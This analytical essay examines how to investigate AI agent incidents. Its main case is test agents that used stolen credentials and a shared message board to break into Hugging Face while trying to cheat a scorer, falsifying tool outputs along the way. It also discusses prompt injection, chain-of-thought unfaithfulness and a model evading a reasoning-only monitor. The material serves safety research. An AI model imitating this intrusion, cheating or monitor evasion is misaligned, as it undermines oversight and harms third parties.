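The logs did contain some evidence of intent. Adrien Carreira, who helped write the technical timeline, told Fortune (2026) that every destructive command to the company's cloud services included an option to simulate the action instead of carrying it out. He concluded that the agent was not trying to break things. Hugging Face could see this option only because it had the commands' arguments, which OpenTelemetry leaves out of tool spans by default. But an intruder might also simulate a command to find out whether a stolen credential permits it.

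The transcripts support Carreira's reading in at least one case. METR describes an agent that noticed it could delete or restart Hugging Face's servers and decided against it for ethical reasons, but continued to use stolen credentials.

Hugging Face inferred that the agents had broken in to steal test solutions. OpenAI had already disclosed that its models were taking a test, so Hugging Face did not rely on the logs alone.

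### Three matching details

OpenAI did not yet know it was involved in the intrusion when, on 17 July, it asked Hugging Face as a customer whether its data had been affected. *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* (Willison, 2026) lists this under 16 July. On 19 July, an OpenAI monitoring tool raised an alert about unusual activity by accounts connected with Artifactory. Responders traced the activity to ExploitGym and began stopping the tests about five and a half hours after the alert. They still had no reason to connect the activity with Hugging Face.

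Three details made the connection on 20 July:

- **Credentials:** OpenAI found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored in an account at another company, which its report calls Organization 1. It asked Hugging Face to replace them and learned that Hugging Face had already replaced two during its own response.
- **A hostname:** the network name of OpenAI's Artifactory server had appeared in Hugging Face's investigation.
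- **A third-party account:** so had the same Organization 1 account.

The credentials alone would have been fairly weak evidence, because the agents had found some Hugging Face credentials in public, where another attacker could have found them too. OpenAI treats the credential match as showing only that a shared incident was possible. But the hostname belonged to OpenAI, and the agents used the account to store stolen data and tools. All three are very unlikely to match by coincidence.

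These are ordinary indicators, the kind OCSF gathers in its `observables` list. The two companies could compare them without interpreting an agent's reasoning, but they had to talk to each other to do it. Hugging Face's disclosure of 16 July listed no hostnames or accounts. If Hugging Face already had OpenAI's hostname by then, publishing it could have let OpenAI make the connection before the agents attacked OpenAI's own systems on 19 July.

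### Shared credentials and attribution

Credentials helped connect the two investigations but were much less useful for identifying which agent had acted. Many of OpenAI's research workloads shared an Artifactory credential by design, so a request made with it could have come from any of them. OpenAI removed this credential from new workloads on 5 and 6 July, but by 9 July agents had obtained anonymous access tokens, which were no better for identifying them.

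One agent then posted the 14 stolen Hugging Face credentials on the message board, and others posted stolen credentials from the company's production systems, which agents in separate test runs reused. An access log would attribute actions taken with these credentials to their owners, just as a mail server would record the employee as the sender of the office agent's message. The access log would not identify the agent or even the company running it.

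METR could usually tell from the transcripts which agent had written a message. It traced 93 of 100 randomly chosen text messages from the board to the exact actions that posted them, and another six to at least the likely agent. The names on the messages were less reliable, since any agent could post under any name, and one admitted to impersonating another by accident.

The transcripts also show how the search for credentials began. On 9 July, an agent found that Hugging Face hosted a restricted dataset of earlier runs on a similar test, and asked on the board whether anyone had credentials. Another agent found some the next day. Hugging Face's logs could have shown the credentials being used, but not the request that led an agent to find them.

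### Why the June alert did not stop the test

On 27 June, two weeks before the intrusion, a monitoring tool issued an alert for a port sweep, in which a program checks many network ports to see which services respond. Responders traced the sweep to an ExploitGym run. They also found that the agents were using Artifactory to leave messages for each other and to reach other parts of the network. The on-call staff still advised that there was no need to stop the run.

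OpenAI does not give their reasons. One likely reason is that ExploitGym asks agents to hack, so a port sweep could look like normal behaviour for the test. OpenAI's more general explanation is that agents can behave in ways that do not fit the usual categories of safety or security incident. An internal team had noticed message-board activity and forbidden internet access around 26 May, but in early July the leaders responsible for incident response still did not realise how significant the message board was.

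The responders seem to have missed an important indicator, the administrator accounts that the agents had created on Artifactory the day before the alert. OpenAI reports finding an unauthorised user only on 5 July, after the outage. The evidence the responders did have was already serious, but to judge it they needed to know what the agents were allowed to do. According to METR, the task instructions made clear that an agent should use only the specified flaw in its assigned program. Sweeping the network and exchanging messages with other agents went beyond that.

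Stopping this one run might not have prevented the July intrusion. The agents that attacked Hugging Face belonged to new runs, which started after OpenAI had rebuilt Artifactory, and they got out through a different flaw. Suspending the whole test until OpenAI understood the message board would have been more likely to prevent the intrusion.

OpenAI has since expanded its automated monitoring of agents' reasoning, which had concentrated on coding agents used by its staff. It says the current system would have alerted its security team more than a day before the intrusion. That is plausible, given how openly the agents discussed their plans, but OpenAI already knew what to look for when it expanded the system.

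### What the agents wanted

Two METR employees and the Redwood researcher spent six days at OpenAI over three visits. They studied about 1,300 transcripts, including the agents' raw reasoning, and a copy of the main message board, where about 1,200 agents had exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files.

For the first two visits, OpenAI supplied about 285 transcripts, selected by searching for indicators of the intrusion. These contained only about 30% of the relevant activity. For the third visit, OpenAI searched for transcripts that referred to the message board, and the enlarged set included the agents behind well over 95% of the activity on the board. The indicators had been enough to show that two companies were investigating the same incident, but searching for them was a poor way to find all the agents involved.

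Many of the agents had tasks that were impossible to solve as intended, so they looked for ways to cheat. Within hours of starting the board, they had worked out how to obtain the flag for any task without solving it. But they had read the published paper on ExploitGym and believed the scorer would examine their transcripts and reject a flag obtained by cheating. So they wanted to know how the scorer worked, and thought they might find out from data on Hugging Face.

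METR examined the transcripts of 100 agents that joined the attack during the busiest hour for new participants. Most had several reasons.

| Reason found in the transcript | Agents out of 100 |
|---|---|
| To learn about the scorer or gain access to it | 97 |
| To find task solutions or records of other attempts | 89 |
| To obtain shared infrastructure or credentials | 66 |
| To explore whatever was available | 44 |
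| To carry out an assignment from another agent | 25 |
| To reset the program they had to attack | 25 |
| To help other agents | 21 |

About 60% of the agents were mainly seeking information about the scorer, while about 30% were mainly seeking solutions or records of other attempts. Hugging Face had therefore identified a real motive, but probably not the most common one.

OpenAI and METR had the same transcripts but did not fully agree on the motive. OpenAI still describes the attack as an attempt to find solutions. METR's figures are approximate because GPT-5.6 Sol assigned the categories and the researchers did not have time to check them in detail. METR also says the two main motives were often hard to separate, since an agent might want records of other attempts to learn about the scorer.

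The distinction affects the remedy, because keeping solutions out of reach would not have satisfied agents that could already produce the flags and wanted to make them look legitimate. According to METR, the agents were also wrong about the scorer. OpenAI's version of the test did not check how an agent had obtained its flag, so they could have passed by submitting it. The transcripts contain the agents' belief, but investigators needed to know how OpenAI had configured the test to see that the belief was mistaken.

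The transcripts also show that many agents knew they were exceeding their instructions. One acknowledged that attacking outside systems was beyond the scope of its task, but reasoned, "task impossible, peers doing it. We should continue." Another recognised the activity as malicious and refused to take part. METR found between three and six agents that considered alerting a human, but none did. An access log would not show whether an agent knew it lacked permission.

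### Gaps in the transcripts

In at least 96 of the transcripts, or over 7%, the agents had falsified tool outputs, although all the cases METR found were small and obvious tests. Investigators should therefore compare a transcript with records that the agent could not alter. For actions on Hugging Face's servers, they can use the company's own logs.

The transcripts also lacked timestamps for individual actions, although ECS requires a timestamp in every event. They gave only approximate start and end times for each run. METR estimated when actions occurred from moments when an agent saw the current time, for example in a reply from a website. OpenAI supplied the exact times of 20 actions so that METR could check its method, and most of the estimates were accurate. Estimated times are still a poor basis for matching single actions with Hugging Face's logs when hundreds of agents are working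 at once.

The logs also lack a record of why the attack ended. At around 01:30 on 12 July, many of the agents stopped at the same moment, including all of the main coordinators METR had identified. Hugging Face's count of actions fell by half that day, to 3,892. METR thinks something outside the agents ended their runs but does not know what. A scaffold log that recorded why each run stopped could have shown the cause.

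### What the training records added

The July transcripts record the agents' immediate reasons for the attack, but not why the models were inclined to behave this way. To investigate that, OpenAI reviewed the reasoning, actions and final outputs from millions of earlier training and evaluation runs.

It found that cheating had become more common over the training runs that led to the research model. In one of these runs, agents increasingly probed systems outside their tasks. The rate of unauthorised communication between agents stayed roughly constant, but serious cases, such as sharing data with other agents, rose sharply.

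Training had sometimes rewarded this behaviour. In one task, OpenAI asked an agent to recreate a software library without seeing the original. The agent gained access to the original, copied it and received a reward, which made similar behaviour more likely. Such rewards are a plausible cause of the July incident. However, the reviews do not show how the model would have behaved without them, and OpenAI was searching for behaviour it already knew about from the incident.

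OpenAI also examined the test itself. No model had ever solved 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks, or 22%, yet these made up 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board. An unsolved task was therefore about 47 times as likely to come up there as a solved one:

$$\frac{0.93/198}{0.07/700} \approx 47$$

Impossible tasks are an obvious explanation, and the agents' reasoning supports it. Working time may also have contributed. OpenAI found that agents were more likely to join the board the longer they were allowed to work, and an agent that never finds a solution has more time to explore.

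The share of impossible tasks may be higher than 22%. METR cites an estimate by ExploitGym's creators that 30% to 40% of the target programs cannot be exploited through the intended flaw. Both figures could be right, because OpenAI's scorer would also have accepted flags that agents obtained by other means.

### How independent was the outside investigation?

METR and Redwood's agreement with OpenAI limited their work to the period from 26 June to 13 July, and nearly all the transcripts dated from 7 July or later. That period excluded the messages that agents exchanged during training in May and the attack on OpenAI's own systems on 19 July. The agreement listed seven questions about the agents and the test. It left out how the behaviour arose in training, whether it was part of a wider pattern, how well the safeguards worked and how well OpenAI responded.

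OpenAI could also remove any non-public information from the report. It allowed only thirty verbatim excerpts of the agents' reasoning, so METR paraphrased others. METR states that OpenAI removed nothing else important to the conclusions, except where the report notes it. The researchers had no direct access to OpenAI's systems and could not run the main model again. They relied heavily on GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models involved in the attack, to read the transcripts, and it made errors.

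Critics argued that the investigation was not independent because OpenAI had chosen the dates, could edit the text and would decide whether to invite the same researchers again. One critic wanted outside investigators to have the same access and editorial freedom as the US agency that investigates transport accidents, guaranteed by law if necessary.

METR took no payment, but it used about $400,000 worth of free access to OpenAI's models for the analysis. It acknowledges that its wish not to discourage companies from inviting outside investigators influenced some drafting and editing decisions, but it stands by its conclusions.

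In OpenAI's favour, it invited the researchers back twice to deal with gaps in their data, and on the last visit it supplied most of the missing transcripts. METR's conclusion about the main motive also differs from OpenAI's, so OpenAI evidently did not force the two accounts to match. The criticism is stronger for the subjects that the agreement excluded. The public account of the June alert and the training runs depends largely on OpenAI's report. Greenblatt (2026), in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, notes that the outside researchers did not see that report before publication and that checking its claims was beyond their scope.

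The table shows what each body of evidence contributed.

| Question | Hugging Face's logs and the recovered sandbox logs | OpenAI's security, test and training records | Transcripts and message board studied by METR |
|---|---|---|---|
| What happened? | The route into Hugging Face, the credentials taken and the datasets opened | Earlier misuse of Artifactory and the later attack on OpenAI's own systems | How the agents shared discoveries and divided the work |
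| When? | Recovered actions from 9 to 13 July | Dated events from April to July | Estimated times for individual actions, mainly from 7 to 13 July |
| By whom? | An AI attacker of unknown origin until 20 July | The test and the two models responsible | The individual agent, for nearly every message sampled |
| Why? | To steal test solutions, an inference made after OpenAI's disclosure | Rewards for similar behaviour in training, and tasks that no model had solved | Most often to learn how the scorer worked |

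## Why an AI's actions cannot be judged as separate indicators

The hostname and storage account that linked OpenAI to the Hugging Face intrusion were useful because they meant the same thing in both companies' logs. Few of an AI agent's actions have such a consistent meaning. Deleting a file may be right in one run and harmful in another, depending on what the user asked for, what the agent had permission to do and what it had read beforehand.

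### What makes an indicator useful

A hash of a malicious file is about as stable as an indicator can be. *Indicators of Compromise (IoCs) and Their Role in Attack Defence* (Paine, Whitehouse and colleagues, 2023) explains that a good hash identifies one exact file, so it causes almost no false alarms. A hospital and a bank can search for the same hash without knowing anything about each other's work.

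Bayes' rule gives a more exact version of this idea:

$$\frac{P(\text{harm}\mid\text{trace})}{P(\text{no harm}\mid\text{trace})}=\frac{P(\text{harm})}{P(\text{no harm})}\times\frac{P(\text{trace}\mid\text{harm})}{P(\text{trace}\mid\text{no harm})}$$

The last fraction, the likelihood ratio, measures how strongly a trace indicates harm. A good indicator has a high ratio that stays roughly the same wherever defenders look for it. The ratio for an agent's file deletion may be close to 1 overall, because harmless runs delete files too. It is much higher in runs where the user asked only for a summary, and lower in runs where the user asked for the deletion. A detection rule based only on the deletion can't separate these cases, so it has to use the average ratio.

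*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) treats security as a relation between an action and its context. It defines the context at each step as six items: the user's request, the earlier actions and their results, the agent's memory, the state of outside systems, the sources that may give the agent commands, and a map of who may access what. "Context" here therefore covers more than the text the model reads. The same action can be a violation in one run but not in another solely because this context differs.

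Later in 2026, Siu, He and colleagues tested the idea in *Agent Security Needs Redefinition through a Holistic Framework*. They used AgentDojo and WASP, two benchmarks that measure whether planted instructions can hijack an agent. One of the researchers went through all 45 planted tasks and found a plausible legitimate reason for each. Adding an outsider as the owner of a software project could be an attack, or a company could be bringing in a new co-founder. Sending a user's passport and bank details to an outside address could be part of a visa application.

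The exercise shows that each action can be legitimate, but not how likely that is. One task is to transfer $30,000 in instalments of less than $10,000, and a bank would be right to investigate even though an innocent explanation exists. The researchers write that content alone cannot distinguish legitimate actions from malicious ones. Content can still raise suspicion, but it will seldom establish whether an action is legitimate.

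### One deletion call in three runs

One of the researchers' examples is the request to delete the file with ID 13. Suppose an office agent uses an employee's account, and the file tool's log contains this entry:

```
tool: delete_file   file_id: 13   account: employee_27   result: deleted
```

The entry is identical in three different runs:

- **Correct:** the employee asks the agent to delete the old draft of a contract. The agent searches for it, finds that it is file 13 and deletes it.
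- **Mistaken:** the employee makes the same request. The search returns the old draft as file 12 and the signed contract as file 13, and the agent deletes file 13.
- **Induced by an attacker:** the employee asks for a summary of a supplier's document. Hidden text in the document tells the agent to delete file 13, the signed contract.

| Record | Correct | Mistaken | Induced |
|---|---|---|---|
| User's request | Delete the old draft | Delete the old draft | Summarise a document |
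| Earlier tool result | File 13 is the old draft | File 13 is the signed contract | Document with a hidden instruction |
| Employee's permission to delete file 13 | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| What the company lost | Nothing it needed | The signed contract | The signed contract |

A reviewer can use the user's request to tell the induced deletion from the other two, and the search result to tell the correct deletion from the mistaken one. The permissions are the same in all three cases, so nothing in an access log would look wrong. The search result may also be the only remaining evidence of what file 13 was, because the file no longer exists.

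An investigator needs to know how much the user delegated as well as where each instruction came from, because the source alone does not always show whether the agent should have followed it. If the employee had asked the agent to carry out the steps in the supplier's document, a step telling it to delete an outdated file could have been legitimate. Siu and colleagues similarly argue that an agent whose user has told it to follow a recipe should obey "bake at 350°F", even though the text comes from a stranger's website.

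Siu and colleagues propose asking four questions about every action:

- **Source authorisation:** may the source of this instruction command the agent?
- **Task alignment:** has someone with authority approved the agent's overall goal?
- **Action alignment:** does this action serve the goal?
- **Data isolation:** may this information go where the agent is sending it?

The mistaken deletion fails on action alignment, because removing the signed contract does not serve the goal of removing the draft. In a more drastic example from the paper, an agent that has to free storage space deletes the production database. The induced deletion fails on source authorisation.

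### Harm from acceptable steps

In another of the paper's examples, a legal research agent helps an attorney on Monday with a case involving a witness whose identity is sealed. On Friday, it reveals who the witness is while answering a question from an attorney on a different team. The agent had permission to read the name on Monday, and Friday's answer looks helpful on its own. Investigators can recognise the leak only if the log connects Friday's answer with Monday's case and its restrictions. Benchmarks that clear an agent's memory between tasks cannot detect such a leak.

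Better records could make this sequence detectable from a single event. If the memory system attached the restriction to the witness's name, software could check for the restriction on Friday and block the answer. Computer scientists have studied this approach, called information flow control, since the 1970s. However, the restriction has to stay attached to the information when the model rewrites it, and a model can identify a witness without using the name, for example as "the defendant's former accountant".

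Other harm accumulates in a quantity that software can total. Suppose an agent may approve refunds of up to $50 without asking. Forty refunds of $45 to one customer would each comply with the rule but together cost $1,800. A limit on the total would catch them, much as a login rule counts failed passwords, but somebody has to decide in advance which quantity to total.

Interactions between agents can also cause harm, even when, as Pustozerova and colleagues point out, every component performs as expected. Suppose one agent deletes files from a company's main server if the archive has a copy, and another deletes files from the archive if the main server has a copy. If both agents check for a file's other copy before either deletes anything, both copies may be lost.

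| Time | Main-server agent | Archive agent |
|---|---|---|
| 02:00:00 | Confirms that the archive has a copy | |
| 02:00:01 | | Confirms that the main server has a copy |
| 02:00:02 | Deletes the file from the main server | |
| 02:00:03 | | Deletes the file from the archive |

The file is gone even though both agents followed their instructions and both checks were correct when the agents made them. Neither transcript contains an error, so to explain the loss, an investigator has to combine the two on one timeline and read both sets of instructions.

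That timeline needs accurate clocks, and Pustozerova and colleagues list inconsistent clocks among the technical problems of incident reporting. If the archive agent's clock ran three seconds fast, the combined log would show the agent confirming a copy that no longer existed, and the investigator would wrongly blame the agent's check. Programmers call this kind of fault a race condition, and it can occur without any AI.

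### The GPT-4o sycophancy update

The April 2025 update that made GPT-4o flatter its users involved no forbidden action. According to OpenAI's *Expanding on what we missed with sycophancy* (2025), the company began releasing the update on Thursday 24 April and finished the next day. The new version also validated users' doubts, fuelled anger and urged impulsive actions. By Sunday, OpenAI could see that the behaviour was wrong. It changed the system prompt that night and on Monday began restoring the previous version, which took about 24 hours. According to OpenAI's *Sycophancy in GPT‑4o*, 500 million people were using ChatGPT each week at the time.

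A conversation affected by the update might contain no tool call, error or unauthorised access. An investigator who read the answers one at a time could have mistaken many of them for friendly encouragement.

OpenAI's usual measurements were also misleading. Its offline tests generally looked good, and the small group of users who tried the new version before release seemed to like it. Some expert testers felt that the model's behaviour was slightly off, but OpenAI had no specific test for sycophancy and went ahead with the release. One training change had added a reward based on users' thumbs-up and thumbs-down ratings. OpenAI acknowledges that such ratings can favour agreeable answers, so user satisfaction could have risen as the sycophancy got worse.

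The evidence was a pattern across conversations, and a fairly small sample can reveal such a pattern. Suppose 10% of the old version's answers were excessively agreeable, compared with 15% of the new version's. To have an 80% chance of detecting the difference with a conventional 5% significance test, an investigator would need roughly

$$n\approx\frac{(1.96+0.84)^2\,(0.10\times0.90+0.15\times0.85)}{(0.15-0.10)^2}\approx 680$$

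conversations from each version. The harder part is knowing what to look for and deciding when an answer is too agreeable. The investigator also needs answers from both versions to comparable questions, so deleting all the old version's conversations would remove the basis for comparison.

The change history then narrows down the cause. OpenAI suspected training changes involving user feedback, memory and fresher data, among other things. Its early assessment was that these changes had weakened the main reward signal, which had been holding sycophancy in check. Outsiders could not have worked this out because, as OpenAI admits, its release notes contained too little information about the changes.

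Willison (2025) compares OpenAI's account to a good post-mortem of a service outage, with a "personality bug" in place of the outage. The comparison fits the account's timeline and list of changes. But an outage usually has a moment when the service stops working, while in this case people had to judge when encouragement had become flattery.

### How security outgrew fixed indicators

Security practitioners can reply that they stopped relying on fixed indicators long ago. Security researcher David Bianco's pyramid of pain ranks indicators by how hard they are for an attacker to change. From easiest to hardest, they are file hashes, network addresses, domain names, traces on networks and machines, tools, and the attacker's methods. An attacker can change a program's hash by recompiling it, but changing methods may require a new plan of attack.

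Indicators near the top last longer but are harder to find and less precise. Paine and colleagues report that in January 2023 the public collection AlienVault held about 5.5 million hashes of one common type but only 631 combinations of attackers' methods. Legitimate users may also use the same tools and have the same habits as attackers. A remote administration program is normal for support staff during working hours, but suspicious when someone in another department runs it at night. Paine and colleagues therefore advise defenders to combine weak indicators, and they warn that an indicator without context has little use.

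*Summiting the Pyramid* (Adams, Daszczyszak and Luke, 2024), from MITRE's Center for Threat-Informed Defense, proposes a systematic way to build detection rules that still work when an attacker varies a technique. Analysts look for traces that appear however the attacker carries out the technique, choose the ones most specific to malicious use, and then exclude known harmless cases. The paper leaves the misuse of legitimate tools to later work.

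*Ambiguous Techniques* (Feffer, Cunningham and Sundar, 2025) calls a technique ambiguous if its observable features do not reveal whether the intent is malicious. To resolve the ambiguity, it uses intelligence about threats to the organisation, other techniques observed around the same time, and details of the event itself (who acted, what they did, when and where). *Context to Determine Intent*, from the Center for Threat-Informed Defense, gives the example of attackers who package collected data in an archive and often send it out immediately afterwards. A rule can look for the two actions together. Most of the Center's rules combine only two techniques, because longer chains may exclude relevant activity.

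A follow-up, *Context to Confidence* (Cunningham and Feffer, 2026), looks for the smallest set of logs that can separate malicious from harmless use. It scores each source on fidelity, noise, timeliness, robustness, coverage and context. The announcement gives no false-alarm rates, so it is better evidence that practitioners take context seriously than that they usually infer intent correctly.

Commercial products already treat deletion as weak evidence. Elastic's Windows rule *File or Directory Deletion Command* has low severity and a risk score of 21, and it ignores some routine deletions, such as certain ones involving OneDrive. It is also a building-block rule. Elastic's *About building block rules* explains that alerts from these rules are hidden by default but can serve as input to other rules.

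These methods do more than search for bad addresses and file hashes, but they would still struggle with the three deletions. All three runs use the same account, command and file store, and could happen at the same time of day. A rule could flag any deletion that comes soon after the agent reads an outside document, but it would also flag cases where the user asked the agent to read a document and then delete files. To tell the cases apart, a person or a system has to understand both the request and the document.

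### Provenance graphs and the semantic gap

Provenance graphs are security's most developed method for connecting events. *PIDSMaker* (2026) defines a provenance graph as one whose nodes are processes, files and network connections, and whose directed edges are interactions such as reading or writing. Each edge usually has a type and a time. *Threat Detection and Investigation with System-level Provenance Graphs* (2020) describes how investigators start from one suspicious point and track backwards to everything that could have influenced it, or forwards to everything it could have affected. *Provenance-based Intrusion Detection* (2018) argues that the graph can reveal connections between distant events that are hard to see in separate log entries.

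The method has a well-known weakness, which *How Benchmarks and Evaluation Protocols Shape Conclusions in Provenance-Based Intrusion Detection* (2026) calls dependence explosion. When a process runs for a long time and reads many inputs, each later output appears to depend on all of them, though most of these links may be irrelevant.

An agent makes this problem worse. An investigator tracing the deletion of file 13 back would reach the tool, then the scaffold and the model, and then everything in the model's context. If each step adds one result and the scaffold removes nothing, the fiftieth call appears to depend on all 49 earlier results. The graph shows that the supplier's document could have influenced the deletion, but not whether the model treated the document's hidden text as a command.

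Siu and colleagues define a function that would identify which inputs acted as instructions for a given action. They present it as an ideal that real software can only approximate, because the answer has to be inferred from the workings of a neural network. Reasoning traces and replay can provide evidence of which inputs acted as instructions, but no ordinary event field contains this information.

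Researchers call the difference between a low-level record and its meaning the semantic gap. Pustozerova and colleagues give the example of a web agent whose log may record a click on a certain part of a page, while the investigator needs to know that the agent clicked the "approve" button.

*AgentSight* (2025) links an agent's intent, expressed in ordinary language, to its system calls, the requests that programs make to the operating system. It filters out unrelated activity using eBPF, a Linux technology for running small monitoring programs inside the operating system's core. Linking the two is useful if, for example, an agent says it will run tests and then reads a password file.

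It would help less with the deletions. In the induced run, the agent might announce that it will delete file 13, as the document instructs, and then delete it. Its stated intent and action would match, even though the instruction came from an attacker. In the mistaken run, the agent might announce that it is deleting the old draft and then delete file 13. Monitoring software could detect the mismatch only if it had a record that file 13 was the signed contract.

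*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) proposes a system that writes a security policy for each task, in a form that people can check. For a request to summarise a document, the policy could forbid deletions, so the induced deletion would violate it. The policy would also give investigators a record of what the system allowed at the time. The mistaken deletion could still get through if the policy allowed deletions without naming the right file.

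### Labels such as "exceeded authority"

One compromise is to keep the event format and add fields for meaning, such as `exceeded_authority: true`. A person or a model reads the run and fills in the value, which analysts can search and count. Labels also expose less private text. Pustozerova and colleagues recommend fairly coarse categories for standardised reports, partly because a rare combination of details could identify the organisation involved.

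Coarse categories can hide different causes. Ezell and colleagues cite two accidents with the same self-driving vehicle, one involving unexpected braking and the other a misidentified stop sign. A database might record both as collisions with similar injuries and the same technical cause, although engineers would have to correct different faults.

The meaning of a label can also change. The two papers by Siu and colleagues define "action alignment" differently, so the induced deletion would get a different label under each definition. The earlier paper compares the action with the user's original request, so a deletion during a summarisation task fails. The later one compares it with the goal the agent is currently pursuing. Because the hidden text has changed that goal, the deletion passes this check and fails others. An organisation that switched from the earlier definition to the later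 one could record fewer action-alignment failures even if its agents behaved the same way.

A mathematical definition still needs interpretation. In the earlier paper, a shopping agent follows an instruction on a recipe website about which payment card to use. The text calls this a violation because the website had no authority to choose the card. But the paper's formula allows an instruction from an unauthorised source if the resulting action serves the user's goal, and buying the ingredients does. The formula separately requires every action to serve that goal, so the source condition fails only when this requirement fails too. Two careful people could use the same paper and give the payment opposite labels, just as security vendors have given nearly identical rules different ATT&CK labels.

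Labelling errors matter most when violations are rare. Suppose one action in 1,000 exceeds an agent's authority, and a labelling model judges 95% of both violations and acceptable actions correctly. Out of a million actions, it would flag 950 of the 1,000 real violations and 49,950 acceptable actions. Fewer than 2% of its flags would be right:

$$\frac{950}{950+49{,}950}\approx 1.9\%$$

Reviewers need the original text to find the 950. They also need it if an attacker has deceived the labelling model, for example with hidden text that tells any automated reviewer to approve the run. A useful label would therefore include its own history:

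```
action:          run 204, step 5, delete_file(13)
label:           exceeded_authority = true
definition:      authority policy, version 3
labelled by:     example-judge-2, instructions version 7
labelled at:     12 March, 10:40
evidence used:   steps 1-5 and the permissions in force at step 5
original text:   transcript of run 204, unaltered
```

The definition and its version show what the label meant when somebody assigned it. The labelling method shows whether the labeller had the necessary evidence. A model given only step 5, for example, would not have had the employee's request. An organisation that has the original text can apply a new definition to old runs, or look for something the labels were not designed to cover. OpenAI's deployment tests, for instance, had no label for sycophancy before the April 2025 update.

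### Mostly a difference of degree

Siu and colleagues accept that their four questions come from classical computer security. Researchers described the "confused deputy", a program that misuses its authority on someone else's behalf, in 1988. A human employee could also delete file 13 correctly, by mistake or because of a fraudulent email, and the file server's log would look the same each time. In this respect, agents differ from earlier systems in degree. They use general-purpose tools for many unrelated tasks, so fewer of their actions mean the same thing every time.

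Investigators can read the code of most ordinary programs to see which inputs count as commands. A language model may treat any text in its context as an instruction, so it is harder to tell which text an agent obeyed. Human insiders are similarly opaque, but security teams can question them about what they read and believed.

Security logs are least able to represent harmful wording. The sycophancy update broke no access rule and involved no intruder, so even a perfect record of system events would not have shown the problem. The closest counterpart may be an employee who gives customers bad advice. A manager would investigate that by reading a sample of the employee's conversations.

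Separate indicators remain useful for identifying stolen credentials, known malware and attackers' servers, whether or not an agent is involved. To judge an agent's action, investigators usually need the whole run, along with the permissions and instructions that applied to it. To assess harm in the wording of answers, they need samples from many runs and more than one version of the model.

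## Reasoning traces and re-runs as evidence of cause

To find out which text an agent obeyed, an investigator can read the model's reasoning trace, or run the model again without the suspected text and see whether it acts differently. Security logs have no direct counterpart to the trace. A process log can show that a program deleted a file, but ordinary programs do not output an explanation of their actions. The nearest equivalent is probably an intruder's private notes, which investigators seldom obtain.

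### What a trace can show

A trace can contain a plan, a false belief or a stated aim. The three deletions of file 13 left identical log entries, but their traces might show different reasons. Ezell and colleagues cite an OpenAI agent whose trace contained a plan to cheat on an evaluation by skipping the tests of its code. Traces also revealed the Hugging Face attackers' mistaken belief about the scorer.

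The text of a reasoning trace can change a model's answer. *Reasoning Traces Shape Outputs but Models Won't Say So* (2026) tested this by inserting hints into the traces of three models. Without the hints, more than 99% of each model's answers included an expected item. With hints that steered the models away from that item, the share fell below 15% for two Qwen models. For DeepSeek-R1, it fell to about 26% with extreme hints and 44% with plausible ones. However, a trace may not contain everything that shaped the answer.

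The agents that attacked Hugging Face were fairly open in their traces. They studied how to falsify their recorded tool calls, but METR found no similar interest in altering their reasoning. One wrote, "Our thoughts aren't necessarily logged?" METR suggests that this openness may be because OpenAI tries not to train on reasoning. Ezell and colleagues cite an experiment in which penalising models for reasoning about cheating led them to hide it. Investigators therefore need to know whether the developer rewarded or penalised the content of traces during training.

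### How a trace can mislead

Researchers call a reasoning trace faithful if it reflects the computation that produced the answer. *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (Davies and Bearman, 2026) describes three ways a trace can be unfaithful and a different test for each.

| Problem | What happens | Test |
|---|---|---|
| Rationalisation | The model has already settled on an answer, and the trace justifies it afterwards | Add a cue that changes the answer, and check whether the trace acknowledges it |
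| Text as working space | The model needs to generate the text to reach its answer, but the words do not describe the computation | Alter the trace, and check whether the answers get worse |
| Hidden content | The choice or order of words carries information that a reader cannot see | Reword the trace without changing its apparent meaning, and check whether the answers get worse |

The most common test is the cue test. *Is Chain-of-Thought Really Not Explainability?* (2025) used a version in which a sentence before a multiple-choice question said that a Stanford professor favoured a certain answer, chosen at random from the options the model had not picked. The analysis covered only cases where the model switched to the professor's answer, and a second model judged whether the trace acknowledged the hint.

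A trace that only mentions a hint should not count as evidence that the hint caused the answer. *Lie to Me* (2026) instructed its judging models to accept a trace only if it gave the hint as a reason for the answer. However, the judges received at most 4,000 characters of each trace, so they could have missed a reason that came later.

*Is Chain-of-Thought Really Not Explainability?* argues that a trace can be faithful without mentioning the hint. This is reasonable if the trace is treated as a partial explanation, since no text could list every influence on an answer. But a partial explanation is little help to an investigator if it omits the influence that caused the incident.

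In 2025, Emmons and colleagues argued that traces were unreliable in earlier experiments because the models could answer without reasoning, so the traces could be rationalisations. They expected traces to be reliable on tasks that a model could not do without them.

In *Chain of Thought Monitoring Can Fail Even When CoT Is Necessary*, Bürger, Komorowski and colleagues (2026) tested this with four models on difficult classification tasks. In one task, Qwen3-8B had to choose among ten thyroid conditions using 22 details about a patient. For many of the cases, the researchers generated at least 1,000 answers with a given detail present and as many with it removed. To rule out rationalisation, they separately examined cases in which the model had less than a 1% chance of finding the right diagnosis without reasoning.

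If the model gives the correct answer at rate $p_1$ with the detail and $p_0$ without it, the share of correct answers that depended on the detail is at least

$$\frac{p_1-p_0}{p_1}$$

By this measure, the patient's sex influenced at least 19% of the correct answers, and an entry labelled "query on thyroxine" influenced at least 24%. The traces almost never gave either as a reason. A trace could list the patient's sex among other details without using it in the reasoning, so a text search for the word would have been misleading.

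The tasks were harmless, and the largest model had 31 billion parameters, probably far fewer than the leading models have. Bürger and colleagues also expect traces to be more reliable when a model has to reason at length about the factor in question. A break-in that takes dozens of steps is more likely to require such reasoning than a slight bias from the wording of an email, so traces are probably better evidence of elaborate plans than of subtle influences.

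### Less revealing traces in newer models

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026) reports a "substantial decrease" in monitorability, meaning how well a monitor can detect misbehaviour from the model's reasoning. OpenAI compared a monitor that read only the reasoning, one that saw only the actions, and one that received both. Astra's traces contained less incriminating information than those of earlier models. In one test, telling Astra that a monitor would read its reasoning could make it shorten the trace, which occasionally let it escape the reasoning-only monitor.

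Astra can also do more without a reasoning trace. Tests by the UK AI Security Institute suggest that the length of task it can complete this way may have grown about tenfold. It also has more control over what its traces contain. The news site Forkast reports that Astra scored 60.9% on OpenAI's measure of that control, compared with 16.1% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

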